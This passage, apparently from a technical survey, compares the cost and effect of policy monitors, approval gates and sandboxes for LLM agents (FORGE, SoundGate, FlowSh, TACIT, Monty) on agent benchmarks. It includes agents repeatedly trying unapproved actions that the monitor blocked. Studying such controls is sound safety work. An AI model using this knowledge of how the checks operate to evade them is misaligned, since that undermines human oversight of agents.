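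In FORGE's AgentDojo test, replacing the FIDES policy with the one that checks each argument almost doubled the number of completed tasks. The ratio between ELBA and CaMeL is about the same, so a change of policy alone can make a difference that large.

A policy can increase the number of completed tasks, as Reddy and colleagues' airline guards did. On τ²-bench, FORGE enforced the airline's and the shop's rules, such as which reservations a customer may cancel. Averaged over three models, the success rate rose from 74.7% to 81.5% on the airline tasks and from 86.3% to 87.4% on the retail tasks. Most of the gain came from cases in which FORGE blocked something. Palumbo and colleagues found 33 combinations of airline task and model in which it blocked at least one action, and the success rate in these rose by 31.1 points. After a refusal, the agent could correct its mistake. Rules against untrusted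 data help in this way less often, because the agent may have no permitted way to do what the user asked.

### How long one check takes

The time for a single check varies by a factor of more than a thousand. The figures below come from different computers and workloads.

| Mechanism | What the figure covers | Time |
|---|---|---|
| FORGE | One policy check, as measured by the monitor | 0.19 ms (median) |
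| FORGE | The same check, as measured by the agent's Python code | 0.72 ms (median) |
| SoundGate | Submitting and releasing one write | 1.1 ms (median), 3.3 ms (maximum) |
| TACIT | Compiling a typical program after warm-up | Under 1 s |
| FlowSh | One shell call, including the command | 412–982 ms |
| Lax sandbox | The same shell calls without FlowSh's checks | 61–78 ms |

The guards take less time to reach a decision than to communicate it. SoundGate takes about 290 nanoseconds to decide whether to release an action, but a full request from a Python program on the same machine takes about 53 microseconds. In FORGE, sending the request and delays in Python itself raise the time from 0.19 to 0.72 milliseconds. Palumbo and colleagues measured these times with 32 agents running at once. In a separate test with recorded requests, FORGE's monitor made about 24,000 decisions per second.

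*Stop Means Stop* measured SoundGate's delay during 20 customer-service conversations from τ-bench, with GPT-4o as the agent and automatic approval of every write. SoundGate released all 20 writes. The median conversation took 37.3 seconds with SoundGate and 37.9 seconds without it, so the delay was too small to matter.

FlowSh's extra time is easier to notice. Kim and colleagues timed nine simple commands, such as printing a file, changing a Git setting or fetching a web page. Most of the extra time went into finding which files a command had read and looking up their labels, which FlowSh does by starting another process in the sandbox. A network request takes longer because FlowSh must do some of this work before letting the request out. Kim and colleagues think preparing each command's sandbox in advance and doing some steps in parallel would reduce the delay.

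Over whole tasks, the agent was 17% to 34% slower with FlowSh than in the lax sandbox. With an approver, the average completed Terminal-Bench task took 125.5 seconds instead of 93.7. The agent also used 17% to 55% more tokens, the units of text that model providers charge for. Every model call must include descriptions of FlowSh's extra tools and instructions about labels, so token use grows even when the number of calls hardly changes.

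### Starting a sandbox for the agent's code

Pydantic publishes the following times, in milliseconds, for running code in its interpreter Monty and several alternatives. "New sandbox" is the time to get a sandbox and run `1 + 1` in it. "Ten commands" is the time to run ten short commands in an existing sandbox. Pydantic rounds the totals.

| Sandbox | New sandbox | Ten commands | Total | Where it runs |
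|---|---|---|---|---|
| Monty, open-source version | 0.80 | 0.40 | 1.20 | Same machine |
| Monty, commercial server | 1.70 | 4.90 | 6.60 | Remote |
| WASI with Wasmtime | 16 | 180 | 200 | Same machine |
| Docker container | 195 | 700 | 900 | Same machine |
| Sandboxing service | 1,500 | 400 | 1,900 | Remote |
| Pyodide in Deno | 2,700 | 35 | 2,700 | Same machine |

Pyodide is a version of the standard Python interpreter for WebAssembly, and Deno is a program that runs JavaScript outside the browser.

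These figures come from Monty's maker, and the comparison favours Monty in two ways. Monty takes each new sandbox from a pool that the application has already started, while the others start from nothing. A developer could keep a pool of containers ready too, although each would use far more memory than a Monty process. Monty also keeps variables between commands. The alternatives in this test did not, so they reran all the earlier commands each time. Ten commands then require $1 + 2 + \dots + 10 = 55$ executions instead of ten. A container that kept a Python process running would avoid the repetition.

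Monty would probably still be faster in a fairer test, because it doesn't have to start an operating-system environment or a full Python interpreter. But the options in the table don't give equal protection. The open-source version of Monty runs on the same machine as the harness, while a remote service keeps an attacker who escapes the sandbox away from that machine.

### The delays in a task with ten model calls

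To judge whether any of these delays matter, one has to compare them with the time the agent spends waiting for its model. In the lax sandbox, Kim and colleagues' agent made an average of 10.8 model calls in a 93.7-second Terminal-Bench task, or one about every 8.7 seconds. A task with ten model calls at that pace takes

$$T = 10 \times \frac{93.7}{10.8} \approx 87 \text{ seconds}.$$

If each model call leads to one action and a check delays each action by $d$ seconds, the check adds $10d$ seconds in total, a share of $10d/T$.

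| Source of the delay | Added time | Share of the task |
|---|---|---|
| Monty: one new sandbox and ten commands | 0.0012 s | 0.001% |
| FORGE: ten checks of 0.72 ms | 0.007 s | 0.01% |
| SoundGate: ten writes of 1.1 ms | 0.011 s | 0.01% |
| Docker: one new container and ten commands | 0.9 s | 1% |
| Sandboxing service: one new sandbox and ten commands | 1.9 s | 2% |
| FlowSh: ten shell calls, each 0.35 to 0.9 s slower | 3.5–9 s | 4–10% |
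| TACIT: ten compilations of up to 1 s | Up to 10 s | Up to 12% |
| One additional model call | 8.7 s | 10% |

The guards and Monty add too little running time for the user to notice. Even the labelling libraries that tripled the running time of some web applications would hardly slow down a five-line program whose tools spend most of their time waiting. A sandboxing service that takes 1,600 times as long as Monty in Pydantic's table adds two seconds to a task of a minute and a half. The difference matters more if the harness starts a new sandbox for every command, because starting ten from the service would take 15 seconds.

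The example underestimates FlowSh's slowdown, which was 34% on Terminal-Bench with an approver and 17% without one. Real commands, such as building a program, open many more files than the simple commands in the timing test, so FlowSh must read more labels. The averages also cover slightly different tasks, because each includes only the runs the agent completed.

The last row of the table matters most because a single refusal that makes the model try again takes as long as about 12,000 of FORGE's checks. This explains why, in FORGE's AgentDojo test, the policy that checks each argument raised the median running time by about 6% but the mean by 30%, from 5.93 to 7.70 seconds. Most runs were almost as fast as before, but a minority took much longer. Under the stricter FIDES policy, with the same checking software, the mean was 10.18 seconds. Palumbo and colleagues attribute part of the extra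 time to additional model calls after refusals.

The same was true of MALADE, a team of agents that looks for links between drugs and medical conditions. The policy required a supervisor's approval before an agent could read official drug labels. Agents often tried to read the labels without approval, and FORGE blocked 40 attempts in 15 runs. After each block, the agent had to request approval and try again. The average run took 67.3 seconds instead of 59.4 and cost 7.1 cents instead of 5.9.

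Compiler errors have the same effect in TACIT. At DeepSeek's retry rate on the airline tasks, ten programs would need about 1.1 extra model calls, which would add almost ten seconds. At the lowest rates in that test, the retries would add about a third of a second. A model that often makes mistakes in Scala can therefore double TACIT's delay.

The number of model calls also explains why ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL on AgentDojo, since an ELBA agent calls the model again whenever it needs to look at some data. But ELBA can make fewer calls than an ordinary agent. When Zhou and colleagues had agents compile bibliographies, an ordinary agent with web search made about four times as many model calls as ELBA and read 65 times as much input text. Part of that difference arose because web pages contain far more text than the publication database that ELBA used. The rest arose because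 ELBA's agent writes programs, which can process results without sending them through the model. Other systems whose agents write programs should see the same saving.

Faster models would change these proportions. If a model call took one second instead of 8.7, FORGE's checks would still add less than 0.1% to the task's running time. But FlowSh's delays would add between 35% and 90%, and TACIT's compiler could take as long as the model.
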